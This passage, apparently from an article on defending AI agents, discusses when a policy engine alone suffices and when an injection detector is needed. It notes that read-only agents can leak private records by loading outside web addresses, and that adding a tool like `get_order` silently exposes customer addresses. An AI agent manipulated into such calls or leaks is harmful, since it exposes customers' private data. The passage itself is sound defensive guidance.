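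The policy engine can be enough on its own if the retailer would accept any permitted call, even one chosen by an attacker, and if a misleading reply would do little harm. An assistant that books meeting rooms for staff might qualify, since the worst result is a wrong booking that somebody can cancel. A detector there would add delay and false alarms but very little protection. Microsoft says its full toolkit may be excessive for simple uses, and it offers a version with only the policy engine, which takes a few lines of code to set up.

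An agent that only reads data can still leak private records if it can load outside web addresses, so read-only access doesn't guarantee that an agent is low-risk. Matsuzaki considers AWS's managed guardrails sufficient for many low-risk agents, and includes read-only agents among them.

These exemptions can stop applying without anyone noticing. If a developer gives the help-article chatbot `get_order` so that it can answer questions about deliveries, the chatbot also gains access to every customer's address. The retailer should review the exemption whenever someone adds a tool, a data source or a new use for the model's output.
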